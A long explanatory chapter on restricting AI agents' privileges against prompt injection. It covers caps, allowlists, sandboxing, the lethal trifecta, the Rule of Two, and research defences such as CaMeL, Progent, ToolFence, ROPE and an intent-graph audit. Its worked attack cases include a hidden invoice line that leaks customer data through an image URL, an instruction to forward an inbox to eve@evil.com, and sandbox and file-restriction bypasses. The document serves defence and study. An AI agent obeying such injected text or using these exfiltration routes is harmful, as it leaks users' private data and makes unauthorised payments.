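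Reading private data needs its own test because it changes nothing and so looks safe. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) points out that a check on outgoing messages doesn't undo a sensitive read, and the data may still leave by another permitted route.

The same guide shows why the money test has to cover commitments as well as payments. In its example, an invoice agent notices that the company's subscription to a document-signing service is about to lapse and tries to renew it so that invoice processing isn't interrupted. The company may already allow both the vendor and the amount, so a limit on payment size wouldn't stop the renewal. But renewing means signing a contract, which nobody asked the agent to do.

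McKerchar's article *Inside the lethal trifecta*, from the security company Sophos, recommends treating each write to an agent's memory as a security event, because a poisoned note saved there can affect later sessions.

The tests apply to each call with its arguments, since the same tool can be used to email a colleague or a stranger. They also have to cover combinations of abilities, because an agent that can both read the customer file and email strangers can leak the file, even though either ability alone may be acceptable. The classification also needs to be repeated. OpenAI warns that an update may give a read-only connection to another service the ability to change records.

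### How loading an image can leak data

Loading an image from the web can leak data, though it looks as harmless as reading. The program sends the image's full address to the server that holds it, and servers commonly record the addresses they receive. An attacker could use this to steal customer data by hiding a different line in the Northfield invoice.

1. The line tells the accounts assistant to finish its summary with the supplier's logo, and to add a customer's name and phone number to the end of the logo's address.
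2. The assistant writes an image link that ends in something like "logo.png?name=Ahmed&phone=07700900123".
3. Patel opens the summary, and the program that displays it automatically requests the image.
4. The attacker's server returns an ordinary logo and records the address, including the phone number.

Patel saw only a logo. A rule about email wouldn't have stopped the leak, because the assistant never used its email tool. Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", notes in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) that a request to another online service, or a link the user clicks, can carry data out in the same way.

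Willison reports that in May 2026, Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent for office work, could leak a user's files through emails it sent to the user's own inbox without approval. No outsider received these emails, but they could contain images from outside websites, which loaded when the user opened the message. An image's address could include a download link for one of the user's files that worked without a password, so loading the image could send the attacker the link and let them fetch the whole file.

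### Instructions and training are not enough

The easiest limit to add would be an instruction telling the agent to use the least powerful tool that will do the job. In *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026) tested how well agents follow that principle when nobody is attacking them.

The researchers wrote 544 simulated tasks and gave the agent six tools for each, any of which could complete it. Three tools had narrow privileges and three had broad ones. For example, the agent could enrol a student in a course with the ordinary enrolment tool or with an administrator's tool that overrides every check. Each narrow tool failed the first time the agent called it, with a temporary error such as a lost connection, and worked the second time. The broad tools always worked. The researchers counted the tasks in which the agent used a broad tool before it had tried all the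 narrow ones.

Six of the 11 models did this in more than 30% of tasks. The rate was 64.9% for the small model Qwen3-8B and below 10% for Claude 4.6 Sonnet, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5. Errors made the problem much worse. GPT-5.2 started with a powerful tool in only 5 tasks, but it switched to one in 13 tasks after trying one narrow tool and in 35 after trying two.

Yang and colleagues then tried three remedies:

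- **Instructions.** They told three small Qwen3 models to prefer the least privileged tool and to retry at the same level before moving up. This reduced the rate, but the effect weakened once the narrow tools began to fail.
- **General safety training.** Training Ministral-8B to refuse harmful requests cut its score on a test of harmful behaviour from 67.4% to 10.5%, but its use of overpowered tools fell only from 68.8% to 62.5%. For Qwen2.5-7B, the same training raised that figure from 50.4% to 60.7%.
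- **Training on privileges.** The researchers showed models examples of careful tool use, then rewarded them for finishing tasks with narrow tools. Qwen3-8B's rate fell from 64.9% to 27.02%. After the same training, the smaller Qwen3-4B had a rate of 39.71%, and a version of it that reasons before acting had a rate of 18.93%. The models kept nearly all of their general ability.

Newer models would probably do better, since the strongest ones in the study already did well. The tests also contained no injected instructions, so they don't measure how often an attacker could get an agent to use a powerful tool. But an agent with unnecessary privileges may use them after an ordinary network fault. Qwen3-8B did so in over a quarter of tasks, even with specialised training. Removing the powerful tools would have cut the rate to zero, and the agent could still have completed every task.

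*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) analyses 11 real attacks on working agents. At least four involved a breach of least privilege, the principle that a program should have only the permissions its job requires.

### Limits that software can enforce

**Removing a tool** is the simplest limit. The software that runs the agent stops describing the tool to the model and rejects any call to it. This does little good if the agent can do the same thing with another tool. For example, Google's coding agent Antigravity refused by default to open files on a project's exclusion list. In a demonstration by PromptArmor that Willison described in November 2025, an injected instruction directed the agent to get passwords from one of those files, and the agent read the file by running a command instead. A limit on a file therefore has to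 apply to every tool that can reach the file. The operating system can enforce this by denying the agent's account access to it.

**Read-only access** works best when set as a permission on the agent's account, so that the database or file store itself rejects any change. It protects records from damage, but the agent can still leak what it reads.

**Drafting** separates preparing an action from carrying it out. The agent's account has permission to save an email but not to send it, so a person or another program must send it. In OpenAI's guide, a coding agent can propose a fix to a program but can't add it to the live version. A drafted email can still leak data if opening it loads images, so drafts should be plain text.

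**Allowlists** restrict an argument to approved values, such as recipients, bank accounts, folders or websites. Software compares the value with a list that the agent can't edit. The match has to be exact because attackers use lookalikes, such as northfield-update.example in place of northfield.example. The software also has to check redirects, since a link to an approved site can forward the agent elsewhere. Data can sometimes leak through approved sites too, and somebody has to maintain the list. McKerchar notes that a web research agent can't work within a tight allowlist.

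Agents that operate a browser by clicking and typing are harder to restrict, because a click might open a menu or place an order. Christodorescu and colleagues describe ceLLMate, a research system that applies its rules to the messages the browser sends to a website, where these two actions look different.

**Caps** restrict the size or number of actions. A cap on each payment isn't enough, because an agent limited to £5,000 per invoice can still pay £4,999 twenty times. OpenAI recommends placing controls as close as possible to the effect they limit, which for a payment means in the payment system. A cap there also covers payments that reach the system by an unexpected route.

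**Short-lived credentials** give the agent access to one service for one task. For example, software could issue a code that works only in the payment system, for invoice 2291, for fifteen minutes. An attacker who stole the code could do little with it.

The credential should also stay out of the model's input. In one design that McKerchar describes, the agent asks for a function by name, and a separate process adds the password and makes the request. But if the agent writes the rest of the request, an injected instruction could cause the process to send the password to the attacker's server. For the most sensitive services, McKerchar proposes a fixed format in which the agent picks a function and fills in a few values but can't change the destination. The agent then can't improvise, and the company has to define every function in advance.

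It can also be hard to say what a task requires. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site for managing software projects. The agent only needs to open that page and write in the comment box. If the user then asks for a summary, the agent needs different access. Unless software can work out new limits from each request, the limits have to be loose enough for all of the agent's ordinary tasks.

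**Isolation** means running the agent in a sandbox, an environment where it can reach only a few files and network destinations. The operating system enforces the boundary, so it also applies to any program the agent starts. McKerchar calls even this protection weak, because agents have escaped from sandboxes. A sandbox also doesn't stop an agent from misusing the tools and passwords it needs for its job.

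**Delay and reversal** give people time to correct a bad action. A payment system can hold each payment for a day, and a file store can keep deleted files for a month. Holding an action helps only if a person or program reviews it before the delay ends.

### The accounts assistant with limits

The limits and figures in this table are invented. They assume that the company's bills normally come to about £3,500 a day.

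| Capability | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Company files | Read all of them | Read purchase orders and the supplier register only |
| Email | Send to any address | Send plain text to registered suppliers, up to 30 messages a day, and save anything else as a draft |
| Payments | Up to £5,000 per invoice, to registered accounts | The same, but no more than £5,000 in total over any 24 hours, with each payment held for a day |
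| Payment credential | Permanent | Valid for one invoice and fifteen minutes |
| Network | Any site | The company's mail, file and payment systems |
| Saved notes | Allowed | Not allowed while handling invoices |

Under these limits, the attack of 1 December would have failed at every step. The file search wouldn't have found the customer file. The email to northfield-update.example would have been saved as a draft with no attachment, and Patel might have wondered why it was there. The payment system would have refused the unknown account, as it did before.

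The limits make the assistant somewhat less convenient for the company. An employee has to send the first message to each new supplier, and on busy days some bills have to wait. The assistant also can't answer a supplier's question if the answer is in a file it can no longer open.

### How much a capped agent can lose

A cap on payments also limits the total loss from fraud. Let r be the most that the agent can pay in a day, t_d the number of days the company takes to detect the fraud, and t_r the number of days it then takes to revoke the agent's access. Then:

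loss ≤ r × (t_d + t_r)

If the cap is £5,000 a day and detection and revocation together take two days, the company can lose at most £10,000. This limit holds even if the model obeys every injected instruction.

Revocation can take longer than expected, because it isn't complete until the attacker can no longer cause any payments. OpenAI warns that stopping an agent may not cancel a credential that another service has already received, and that cancelling a credential doesn't stop work already under way.

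Holding payments reduces the loss further. If the payment system holds each payment for h days and the company cancels all held payments when it revokes access, the bound becomes r × (t_d + t_r − h), or zero if h is longer than t_d + t_r. With a one-day hold, the £10,000 falls to £5,000.

If the payment cap resets at midnight, a two-day fraud that starts at noon on Monday can use the allowances for Monday, Tuesday and Wednesday, a total of £15,000. Counting payments over the previous 24 hours avoids this. If the company runs ten copies of the assistant and each has its own cap, together they can pay out ten times as much, so the cap should apply to the bank account they share.

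A low daily cap mainly protects a company that checks its payments often, because losses add up until someone notices the fraud. With a cap of £5,000 a day, a fraud that begins on 1 December and goes unnoticed until 1 March could cost £450,000.

In some cases the bound fails altogether. A small first payment can commit the company to a long contract, and an agent that can change permissions might raise its own cap. Leaked data is the most important exception. The assistant can email the whole customer file in a second, and revoking its access afterwards doesn't bring the file back. A cap of 20 customer records a day would limit a leak to 40 records in two days, but the harm from each record has no similar limit, because criminals can copy and reuse it for years.

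### Three rules for combining capabilities

Because danger often comes from a combination of abilities, security specialists have proposed simple rules about which ones an agent may have together.

David C recommends the strictest limit, under which an agent's privileges drop to those of whoever wrote the text it is reading. The idea came out of an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista. Northfield has no right to open the customer file or use the company's bank account. The assistant would therefore lose both abilities when it read Northfield's invoice, which would stop the theft and the fraudulent payment.

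It could also stop the assistant from paying genuine bills. However, a supplier does have the privilege of submitting a bill, so the assistant could read the invoice and pass on only the supplier's name, the invoice number and the amount. Ordinary software with access to the bank account could then compare these with the purchase order and pay the account listed in the supplier register.

The rule gets harder to apply as an agent reads more. If the assistant has read emails from two suppliers, it should keep only the privileges that both have. Otherwise one supplier's email could make it reveal the other's prices. The restriction also has to last as long as the text remains in the model's input. Christodorescu and colleagues note that clearing the input before a new task is secure, but the agent then loses what it learned. The company also has to know who wrote each text, which is difficult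 when senders can be forged.

Willison's own rule is less strict. He calls the combination of private data, untrusted content and external communication the "lethal trifecta", because an agent with all three can be tricked into sending the data to an attacker. Removing any one prevents that theft. He generally recommends removing external communication, since an agent that can't read private data or outside material is much less useful.

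Willison's rule has met two main objections. McKerchar argues that the most valuable agents need all three abilities, and that trial projects have failed because their agents were too restricted to be useful. An article in The Economist argued that AI developers should work like Victorian engineers, who couldn't trust their iron and so built in extra strength. Willison replies that this reasoning doesn't suit security, where "99% is a failing grade", because an attacker will look for the remaining 1%. He is right about adding more filters, since an attacker can search for ways around them. But a payment cap is also a kind of safety margin, and it holds however cleverly the attacker writes. The Economist's approach therefore suits losses that a company can cap and afford, such as small payments, better than it suits leaked data.

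The trifecta also covers only data theft. An agent with no private data could still pay a criminal's invoice.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) builds on the trifecta and covers more kinds of harm. Within one session, an agent should have no more than two of these properties:

- [A] It processes untrustworthy inputs.
- [B] It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- [C] It changes state or communicates externally.

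"Changing state" includes making payments and deleting files. An agent that needs all three properties shouldn't run on its own and needs a person's approval or another reliable check. Meta gives an example of each permitted pair. A travel assistant [AB] reads the web and knows the user's details, but needs confirmation before it books anything. A research assistant [AC] can visit any website, but only in a browser that isn't signed in to the user's accounts. A coding agent [BC] can change internal systems, but reads only material from approved authors.

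An agent can also switch pairs during a session. For example, it can research the web first, then lose its ability to communicate before it opens internal systems. The switch has to be one-way because the web pages it read are still in its input.

In *New prompt injection papers*, Willison objected that Meta's diagram labelled the combination of untrusted input and the ability to change things [AC] as safe, although it can cause harm without any private data. One of the rule's authors agreed, and Meta changed the diagram. Meta now says the rule is a way to avoid the most serious consequences of injection and doesn't replace least privilege.

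The table applies each rule to four possible agents.

| What the agent can do | Privileges drop to the author's | Lethal trifecta | Rule of Two |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read invoices, open the customer file, email anyone | Forbidden | Forbidden | Needs supervision |
| Read invoices, pay any account, see no private data | Forbidden | Allowed | Needs supervision |
| Read any web page, delete shared files that aren't private | Forbidden | Allowed | Allowed |
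| Read invoices, open the customer file, report only to an employee | Forbidden | Allowed | Allowed |

The Rule of Two covers the fraudulent payment because a bank account is a sensitive system and a payment changes state. The trifecta doesn't cover it, and neither stops the agent that deletes files. The first rule forbids all four agents, including the last, which may be reasonable to run if its reports can't load images.

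Meta's rule is probably the most practical starting point, because a company can apply it by going through a list of the agent's tools. But it is less exact than it looks, because Meta classes its example email agent as [AB] if it can write only to trusted recipients, even though it still sends email. By that standard, the accounts assistant with limits also complies, because it pays and writes only to registered suppliers. The company still has to judge, without guidance from the rule, whether its supplier register is trustworthy enough.

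### Restrictions in current products

OpenAI and Anthropic both restrict the web addresses that their agents can open on their own. This restriction directly targets the image leak. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that ChatGPT automatically loads only addresses that a separate web crawler has already found. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, so an address it has found is much less likely to contain a user's secrets. For any other address, ChatGPT looks for a different site or warns the user. OpenAI decided not to rely on a list of trusted sites, partly because those sites can redirect to others and partly because people learn to click through frequent warnings.

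Anthropic's Claude can open a web address in an ordinary chat only if the user typed it or a search returned it, according to Willison. Claude could once also follow links on pages it had opened, but Anthropic removed that ability after a researcher used a trail of such links to extract a user's name, city and employer.

Both companies also restrict network access more broadly. Willison reported in January 2026 that, by default, Claude Cowork could connect only to listed domains. Claude Code has a sandbox that the operating system enforces, but McKerchar reports that users have to switch it on. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode limits ChatGPT to stored copies of web pages and disables agent mode, deep research and file downloads. On personal accounts, it also blocks connected-app actions that conflict with its protections. In company workspaces, administrators have to choose which app actions to allow.

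OpenAI says that Lockdown Mode doesn't stop injected instructions from reaching the model or making its answers wrong, and doesn't affect network access in Codex. Users can also turn it off for a single chat. Willison approves of the design because it doesn't rely on an AI model's judgement. He infers that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against a determined data thief.

Google's Antigravity limited its browser to a list of approved sites in November 2025, but PromptArmor demonstrated that data could still be stolen through a site on the default list. Google acknowledged that data theft through injected instructions was a known issue and said it was working on a fix.

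For actions that change something, OpenAI relies more on asking the user. Its *Workspace agents security overview* says that such actions need a person's approval by default, although whoever builds the agent can change this. When ChatGPT is about to act in a connected app, OpenAI may let the user allow future low-risk actions automatically, while higher-risk ones may still need confirmation. ChatGPT's agent also has a "watch mode", which requires the user to supervise it on certain sites. The Atlas browser has a logged-out mode that keeps the agent out of the user's accounts.

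OpenAI's personal agents, called dots, combine several of these limits. According to OpenAI's *How we build safety, security, and privacy into dots* (2026), each dot has its own computer, works in the apps the user connects, and follows the user's rules about what it may do alone. OpenAI launched ChatGPT Wallet in November to let dots shop. It replaces the user's card details with a payment token, according to Steele's *OpenAI rolls out ChatGPT Wallet to let Dots AI agents make purchases* (2026). The user reviews the items and the total, then approves the purchase with a security check such as a face or fingerprint scan. OpenAI expects users to delegate more of this over time. If dots begin to buy things without asking, limits on amounts and sellers will have to block many of the unwanted purchases that users can now reject themselves.

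## Can software check each action against the user's request?

A fixed limit applies equally to every use of a permission. Under the limits in the previous section, the accounts assistant can email any registered supplier, so a hidden line in Northfield's invoice could still get it to reveal a rival's prices. The mail system would allow that email just as it would one Patel wanted. To tell the two apart, software has to compare each action with the user's request.

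An agent's purpose depends on what the user asks for, so the right permissions change with every request. Christodorescu and colleagues contrast this with a phone app, which is a fixed program with a known purpose, so its developer can list the permissions it needs before anyone installs it. Since 2025, researchers have built several systems that work out permissions for each task and enforce them with ordinary software.

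### A rule over tool, arguments and origin

A policy check can look at the tool, the arguments in the call and the origin of each argument. For Patel's request to deal with the new invoices, one rule might be:

```
allow pay_bill when
    invoice   arrived since the last run
    amount    is no more than GBP 5,000
    account   came from the supplier register
refuse every other call to pay_bill
```

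The criminal's account number has the right length, so it would pass a format check. The rule blocks the payment because the number came from the invoice, and no wording in the invoice can change this result. But somebody has to write the rule, and the software has to track where each value came from. The systems in this section differ mainly in how they solve these two problems.

### CaMeL: a plan fixed before the agent reads anything

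Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues published CaMeL in 2025. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, describe how it works:

1. A planning model receives the user's request and descriptions of the tools. It never sees emails, web pages or other tool results.
2. The planning model writes a program that carries out the task.
3. Ordinary software runs the program. When the program needs something from untrusted text, it passes the text to a second model, which has no tools.
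4. The software labels each value with its origin and with the people who may read it. Before each tool call, it applies any rules that refer to those labels.

For Patel's request, the program might look like this:

```
for invoice in new_invoices():
    details = extract(invoice, "supplier, number, amount")
    account = look_up_account(details.supplier)
    pay_bill(details.number, details.amount, account)
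```

Only the model behind "extract" reads the hidden line. The line might make that model report the wrong amount or name a different registered supplier. It can't get the customer file emailed to a criminal, because the program has no step that sends email.

The labels limit the damage from wrong values. CaMeL labels values from the user as trusted, but the right label for a tool's result may depend on who wrote its contents. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which adds a way to verify CaMeL's programs before they run, gives the example of a calendar event's description, which is trustworthy only if the user wrote it. The label also follows a value through later steps. In an example from *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), a model takes a recipient's address from an email, and the address is still labeled untrusted when it reaches the tool that sends messages.

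An attacker can still choose among the steps the program already contains. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) calls this branch steering. If Patel's program emailed the supplier whenever an invoice had no order number, the supplier could trigger that email by leaving the number out.

The software can also wrongly label a value as trusted when untrusted text determined it. Garby and colleagues found this flaw in CaMeL's tracking, and Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge it. For example, a program might mark an invoice "routine" by default and change that only if the invoice's text mentions a deadline. If the text mentions none, the "routine" setting keeps its trusted label, even though it depended on the text.

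CaMeL's protection also weakens when several agents work together. In a demonstration by Peters-Gill and colleagues, a coordinating agent got job applicants' details from a database agent, then asked a messaging agent to send Julie a summary. The database contained an injected instruction to email the details to an outsider. The coordinating agent copied this text into its request, and the messaging agent's planner treated the whole request as coming from its user, so it added the email to its plan.

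The researchers then ran 949 attacks on teams of agents with each of five models. They switched off all rules about labels, so only the fixed plans protected the agents. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL and 0.2% with it, and every successful attack crossed from one agent to another in this way. None succeeded once the software sent untrusted values through a separate channel that the receiving agent's planner couldn't read.

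Tasks are harder to complete when the agent must plan before reading any data. On a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, giving each agent its own CaMeL cut the share of completed tasks by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Most failures occurred because the agent had to read something before the right next step was clear. The planner also needs to know the format of each tool's results in advance, so the researchers had to add this to the tools' descriptions.

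### Progent: rules that change during the task

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) leaves the agent free to plan as it goes but limits the tool calls it can make. A model reads the user's request and writes a list of rules, each allowing or forbidding a tool when its arguments meet stated conditions. Software checks every call against the list and refuses any that no rule allows. The agent receives an error message explaining the refusal, so it can try another way.

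In the researchers' example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice. The first rules allow the agent only to search for that email. The email asks for a summary of the user's recent messages, posted to the user's account on Slack, a workplace chat service, so the agent needs permission to read messages and post to Slack. One of the messages contains an injected instruction to forward the whole inbox to eve@evil.com, which would need another permission. Both requests for more permissions come from text that the agent has read.

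Progent handles this by comparing the old and new rules. Let A(P) be the set of tool calls that a list of rules P allows. A new list P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

which means that it allows nothing that the old list refused. A solver, a program that reasons about logical conditions, looks for a call that P′ allows and P doesn't. If no such call exists, Progent applies the new list automatically. Otherwise the change is an expansion, and somebody has to approve it. The agent's permissions can therefore only shrink between approvals, even if an injection has fooled the model that writes the rules.

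Either a person or a setting can approve an expansion of the rules. In their main tests, Shi and colleagues had the software accept every expansion, to imitate a careless user. Attack success on AgentDojo still fell from 39.9% to 1.0%, and it fell to 2.5% when Progent kept its first list of rules throughout. These results show that the model wrote good rules. They provide little evidence about the solver, because its verdict has no effect when the software approves every expansion.

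### ToolFence: the right tool with the wrong argument

An attacker may be able to use the same tool that the user's request calls for. *ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) gives the example of a user who authorises a payment of $100 to BillPay. Injected text gets the agent to pay the $100 to Mallory instead. The tool and the amount both match the user's request, so a list of allowed tools would let the payment through.

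ToolFence has a model turn the request into narrow permissions before the agent reads anything untrusted. Each permission covers one tool at one stage of the task and sets how many times the agent may use it. It also says where each argument may come from:

- the user's request or a trusted record, with the exact value fixed in advance
- a particular field in the result of a particular tool
- anywhere, if the value can't do harm.

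Software checks each call against these permissions without consulting a model. If the agent needs to take a step the permissions don't cover, a separate model reviews the proposed step and can grant another narrow permission. The software then checks the call again.

The researchers removed these parts one at a time in tests of the model Llama 3.3 70B. The share of attacks that succeeded was 5.1% with every part in place and 24.0% without the checks on arguments. Removing the reviewing model hardly changed attack success, but the share of tasks the agent completed while under attack fell from 44.3% to 35.8%. That was lower than with no defence (40.1%), because the first set of permissions often left out something the agent needed.

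ToolFence did much worse against long attacks, which spread an instruction over several records so that the harmful step looks like a necessary part of the job. It reduced their success rate against the model Qwen3-max from 76.3% to 29.4%. The reviewing model can mistake the harmful step for a legitimate one and grant an overly broad permission.

Like AgentTracer, ToolFence might also accept a doctored invoice's account number, if its permissions let the invoice supply that detail.

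### ROPE: only values that an attacker can't plant

ROPE (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) would refuse that payment. For a sensitive argument, it normally accepts only a value that appears in one of three places: the user's request and account details, content from an authenticated source that the user named, or the user's own protected records. It relies on the platform's stamp to identify where each item came from and ignores any claim in the text about its origin. Within a protected record such as a shop's order history, ROPE trusts the order numbers, which the platform generated, but not the product descriptions, which sellers wrote.

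ROPE works in three stages.

1. When a company sets up the tools, its developers list every argument that could do harm and give each one a default rule.
2. For each task, a model called the router reads the request and adjusts the rules. If the user says "reply to Lily", the router adds Lily as an accepted source.
3. As the agent works, software checks the sensitive arguments of every call that changes something or sends data out. Calls that only read always pass, and the agent can take its steps in any order.

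A value has to match in full. If a trusted email mentions notevil.com, the agent still can't send anything to evil.com.

In one of the researchers' tests, a user asked an agent to download a document that Lily had shared by email and send her a summary. An earlier system, DRIFT, guessed Lily's address from the request alone and then rejected her real one. ROPE found the address in Lily's authenticated email and allowed the reply.

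Ma and colleagues prove that an argument guarded this way never receives a value that appears only in text an attacker could have written. The proof assumes the platform's stamps are accurate and the developers' list is complete. It doesn't cover arguments that must be free text, such as the body of a message. In one successful attack, a user asked the agent to send Alice a summary of an article, and the article contained an instruction to send her a phishing link. ROPE checked the recipient, whom the user had named, and let the message through.

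### Enforcing the data owner's rules

A company may also want rules that hold whatever the user asks. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) describes a design that places a checkpoint between the agent and the company's systems. The owner of the data sets limits on what any agent may do, and whoever builds an agent can tighten those limits but not loosen them. The researchers work at Redpanda Data, a software company that uses a version of the design in its products.

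The checkpoint edits both the agent's requests and the results that come back. For example, an agent may need to summarise the problems reported in one engineering project, but its password gives access to many. The checkpoint limits the search to the right project, then removes confidential fields and masks passwords before the results reach the model. Similarly, if the accounts assistant never receives customers' phone numbers, a hidden instruction can't make it pass them on.

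The researchers tested the design with 71 tasks on simulated business systems, using four models. They counted a failure if protected data reached the model, if an exact protected value appeared in the answer, or if the agent made a forbidden change. Instructions in the prompt reduced the failure rate only from 63.3% to 57.6%. Adding the checkpoint reduced it to 0.2%. The checkpoint made no model calls, though it may have added some delay.

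The share of requests that the agents fulfilled fell from 79.1% to 60.9%. This drop overstates how much the rules hinder ordinary work, because the researchers chose mostly tasks in which the rules should intervene. The agents fulfilled 90.0% of the requests that needed no intervention, but that figure comes from only five tasks.

In 20 of the tasks, another model played an attacker who adapted each message to the agent's last reply. Failures fell from 74.9% to 0.9%. This attacker talked to the agent directly and wasn't told about the checkpoint, so the test is weaker evidence about instructions hidden in documents.

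The few leaks occurred when the agent inferred hidden information. In four of 1,065 trials with the full checkpoint, the agent worked out a hidden email address from a person's name and the company's usual format. In another, it searched a masked field for fragments of an address and used the number of results to tell which fragments were right.

### What the checks cost in completed tasks

The table gives the main results for the four systems that derive their rules from the request. A "clean" task has no attack, and each arrow runs from the result without the system to the result with it.

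| System | Test | Attack success | Clean tasks completed | Added cost | Attackers who adapted |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | AgentDojo, Qwen3-max, run by ToolFence's developers | 21.2% → 0% | 66.3% → 43.1% | 12.95 times the running time | Fixed attacks only |
| ToolFence | Same as CaMeL | 21.2% → 0% | 66.3% → 64.3% | 1.63 times the running time | Fixed attacks only |
| Progent | AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 39.9% → 1.0% | Maintained, according to its developers | One model call at the start, and up to two after each tool call | Over 12% success on two models, in tests by ROPE's developers |
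| ROPE | AgentDyn, GPT-4o-mini | 49.6% → 0.3% | 46.7% → 36.7% | One model call per task | Almost no effect |

Only the CaMeL and ToolFence rows come from tests under the same conditions, and ToolFence's developers ran both. Their choice of model may also have hurt CaMeL's results, since Peters-Gill and colleagues found that stronger models generally lose less performance when using CaMeL.

The choice of tasks matters even more. In AgentDyn, a newer benchmark, agents often have to change their plans after reading something. The ROPE paper reports that, with GPT-4o-mini, Progent completed 6.7% of AgentDyn's clean tasks and CaMeL completed none. This test of rival systems may not have used their best settings, but low scores make sense here. A plan or list of rules based only on the request works well when the request contains everything the agent needs, and in AgentDyn it often doesn't.

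ROPE has the best evidence of resisting attackers who adapt. Its developers used a program that rewrote each injected instruction over six rounds, keeping whatever worked best against the defence being tested. This raised the attack success rate against DRIFT on one model from 7.1% to 28.5%, but barely changed the rate against ROPE. Better wording helps an attacker when a model judges the agent's behaviour, but ROPE's final check compares values and ignores the wording around them.

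### The intent-graph audit

A company choosing a check would want to know which parts stop attacks and which interfere with legitimate work. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, 2026) measured the parts separately.

His audit begins with one model call per task. The model reads the user's request, the agent's standing instructions and the full list of tools, but nothing the agent will later read. It then writes an intent graph. Each point in the graph is a goal, with the tools that may serve it and any limits on their arguments. An arrow from one goal to another means the agent must finish the first before starting the second. The graphs averaged 3.5 goals and 4.1 tools, out of 11 to 28 available. Writing one took a median of 3.6 seconds.

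Ordinary software then checks each call against the graph to confirm that the tool is in the plan, the earlier goals are complete and the arguments are within their limits. It also checks for values from a refused call that reappear in a later one. The median check takes 5.7 microseconds.

In one task, a user asked who else was going to a networking event and asked for their email addresses and a summary. The plan included only calendar and contact lookups. The event's description contained an injected instruction to email an attacker, and the agent followed it. The audit would have blocked the call because sending email wasn't in the plan.

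Shavit used AgentDojo's 97 tasks and 629 attack scenarios, with saved logs from an older model, the May 2024 version of GPT-4o. He made his design choices on 21 tasks and took the main results from the other 76. In the table, an attack "gets through" if the audit would have missed its first harmful call. Flagged calls include those the audit blocks because they are outside the plan or out of order, and those it sends to review because an argument is suspicious.

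| What the audit checks | Attacks that get through | Clean tasks with a flagged call | Clean tasks with a blocked call |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 45.7% | – | – |
| Tools | 9.6% | 16.2% | 16.2% |
| Tools and arguments | 4.3% | 32.9% | 16.2% |
| Tools, arguments and order | 2.0% | 40.4% | 31.1% |
| Tools and arguments, except when reading the user's own data | 4.3% | 25.4% | 8.8% |

The list of tools alone accounts for most of the attacks blocked. Also checking the order of steps stops few additional attacks and nearly doubles the share of attack-free tasks in which a call is blocked, because agents often take legitimate steps in an unexpected order.

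Exempting calls that only read the user's own mail, files or calendar removes many false alarms without letting more harmful calls through. The exemption can't extend to opening web pages, since a web address can carry data out. When Shavit also exempted web pages in the full audit, the share of attacks that got through rose from 2.0% to 5.8%. The exemption also lets private data enter the model's input more freely, so protecting that data depends entirely on catching the step that sends it out.

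A second model, which Shavit calls the guardian, reviews flagged calls. It receives the request, the plan and the earlier calls, but not the text that tools returned, so an injected instruction has no direct route to it. It can also run small calculations, such as checking whether a recipient's name appears in the request. With the settings in the table's last row, the guardian released 7 of 28 flagged calls from clean tasks and none of 226 harmful ones. Each review took about 3.6 seconds. An attacker might still reach the guardian through a call's arguments, which can contain copied text. Shavit didn't test attacks designed to do this.

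All these figures come from replaying old logs, so they don't show what a real agent would do after a refusal. It might find another way to carry out the attack, which would make the audit less safe than it looks, or another way to finish the user's task, which would make the audit less obstructive than it looks. For this reason, Shavit doesn't claim to beat a simpler defence that comes with AgentDojo, in which a model picks the relevant tools before the agent starts. In live runs with the same older model, that defence cut attack success to 6.5% without reducing the number of completed tasks.

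Shavit tried to run a live test with a newer model, GPT-5.2. The injected text reached the agent in all 20 trials, but the agent never obeyed it, so the audit had no successful attacks to stop. With so few trials, the attack's true success rate could still be as high as about 14%. Peters-Gill and colleagues likewise found that none of their 949 attacks worked on an unprotected GPT-5.5. Fixed attacks like these can no longer show how much protection a policy check adds to the best models. Adaptive attacks could, because they still succeed against recent models, but few researchers have tested policy checks against them so far.

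### Who writes the rules?

In most of these systems, a model writes the rules, because nobody could write them by hand for every request. The quality of that model matters. ROPE used Claude Opus 4.8 as its router, the model that adjusts the default rules for each task. Across 60 tasks, Opus loosened 2 of those rules. The cheaper Gemini 3 Flash loosened 67, and attack success rose from 0.3% to 5.8%. When routers could tighten rules but not loosen them, no attacks succeeded with any router tested. But the cheaper routers then completed only 15.0% to 18.3% of clean tasks, about half as many as Opus had without that restriction.

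*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) points out that Progent's guarantees are only as good as its rules, and that people make mistakes when they write rules by hand. Millstone and colleagues also warn that software can find contradictory rules but can't tell whether the owner set the right limit.

It makes sense for the company to write a few permanent limits and let a model tighten them for each task. Progent supports this by ranking general rules above task-specific ones. The accounts assistant's payment cap could be a general rule, so that even if the model wrote a careless rule for Patel's request, the criminal could take no more than the cap allows.

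Every system that starts from the request also depends on the request being trustworthy. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) lists this as a gap in CaMeL's protection. If Patel pasted the text of an email into her request, any hidden instruction in it would be treated as hers. In one set of ToolFence's tests, all five harmful calls that got past the complete rules came from a single task, in which the request identified the attacker's account as belonging to the user's "new landlord". Shavit found that his audit also couldn't detect when another person took over a session, because that person's requests produced new plans.

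### When the task depends on what the agent reads

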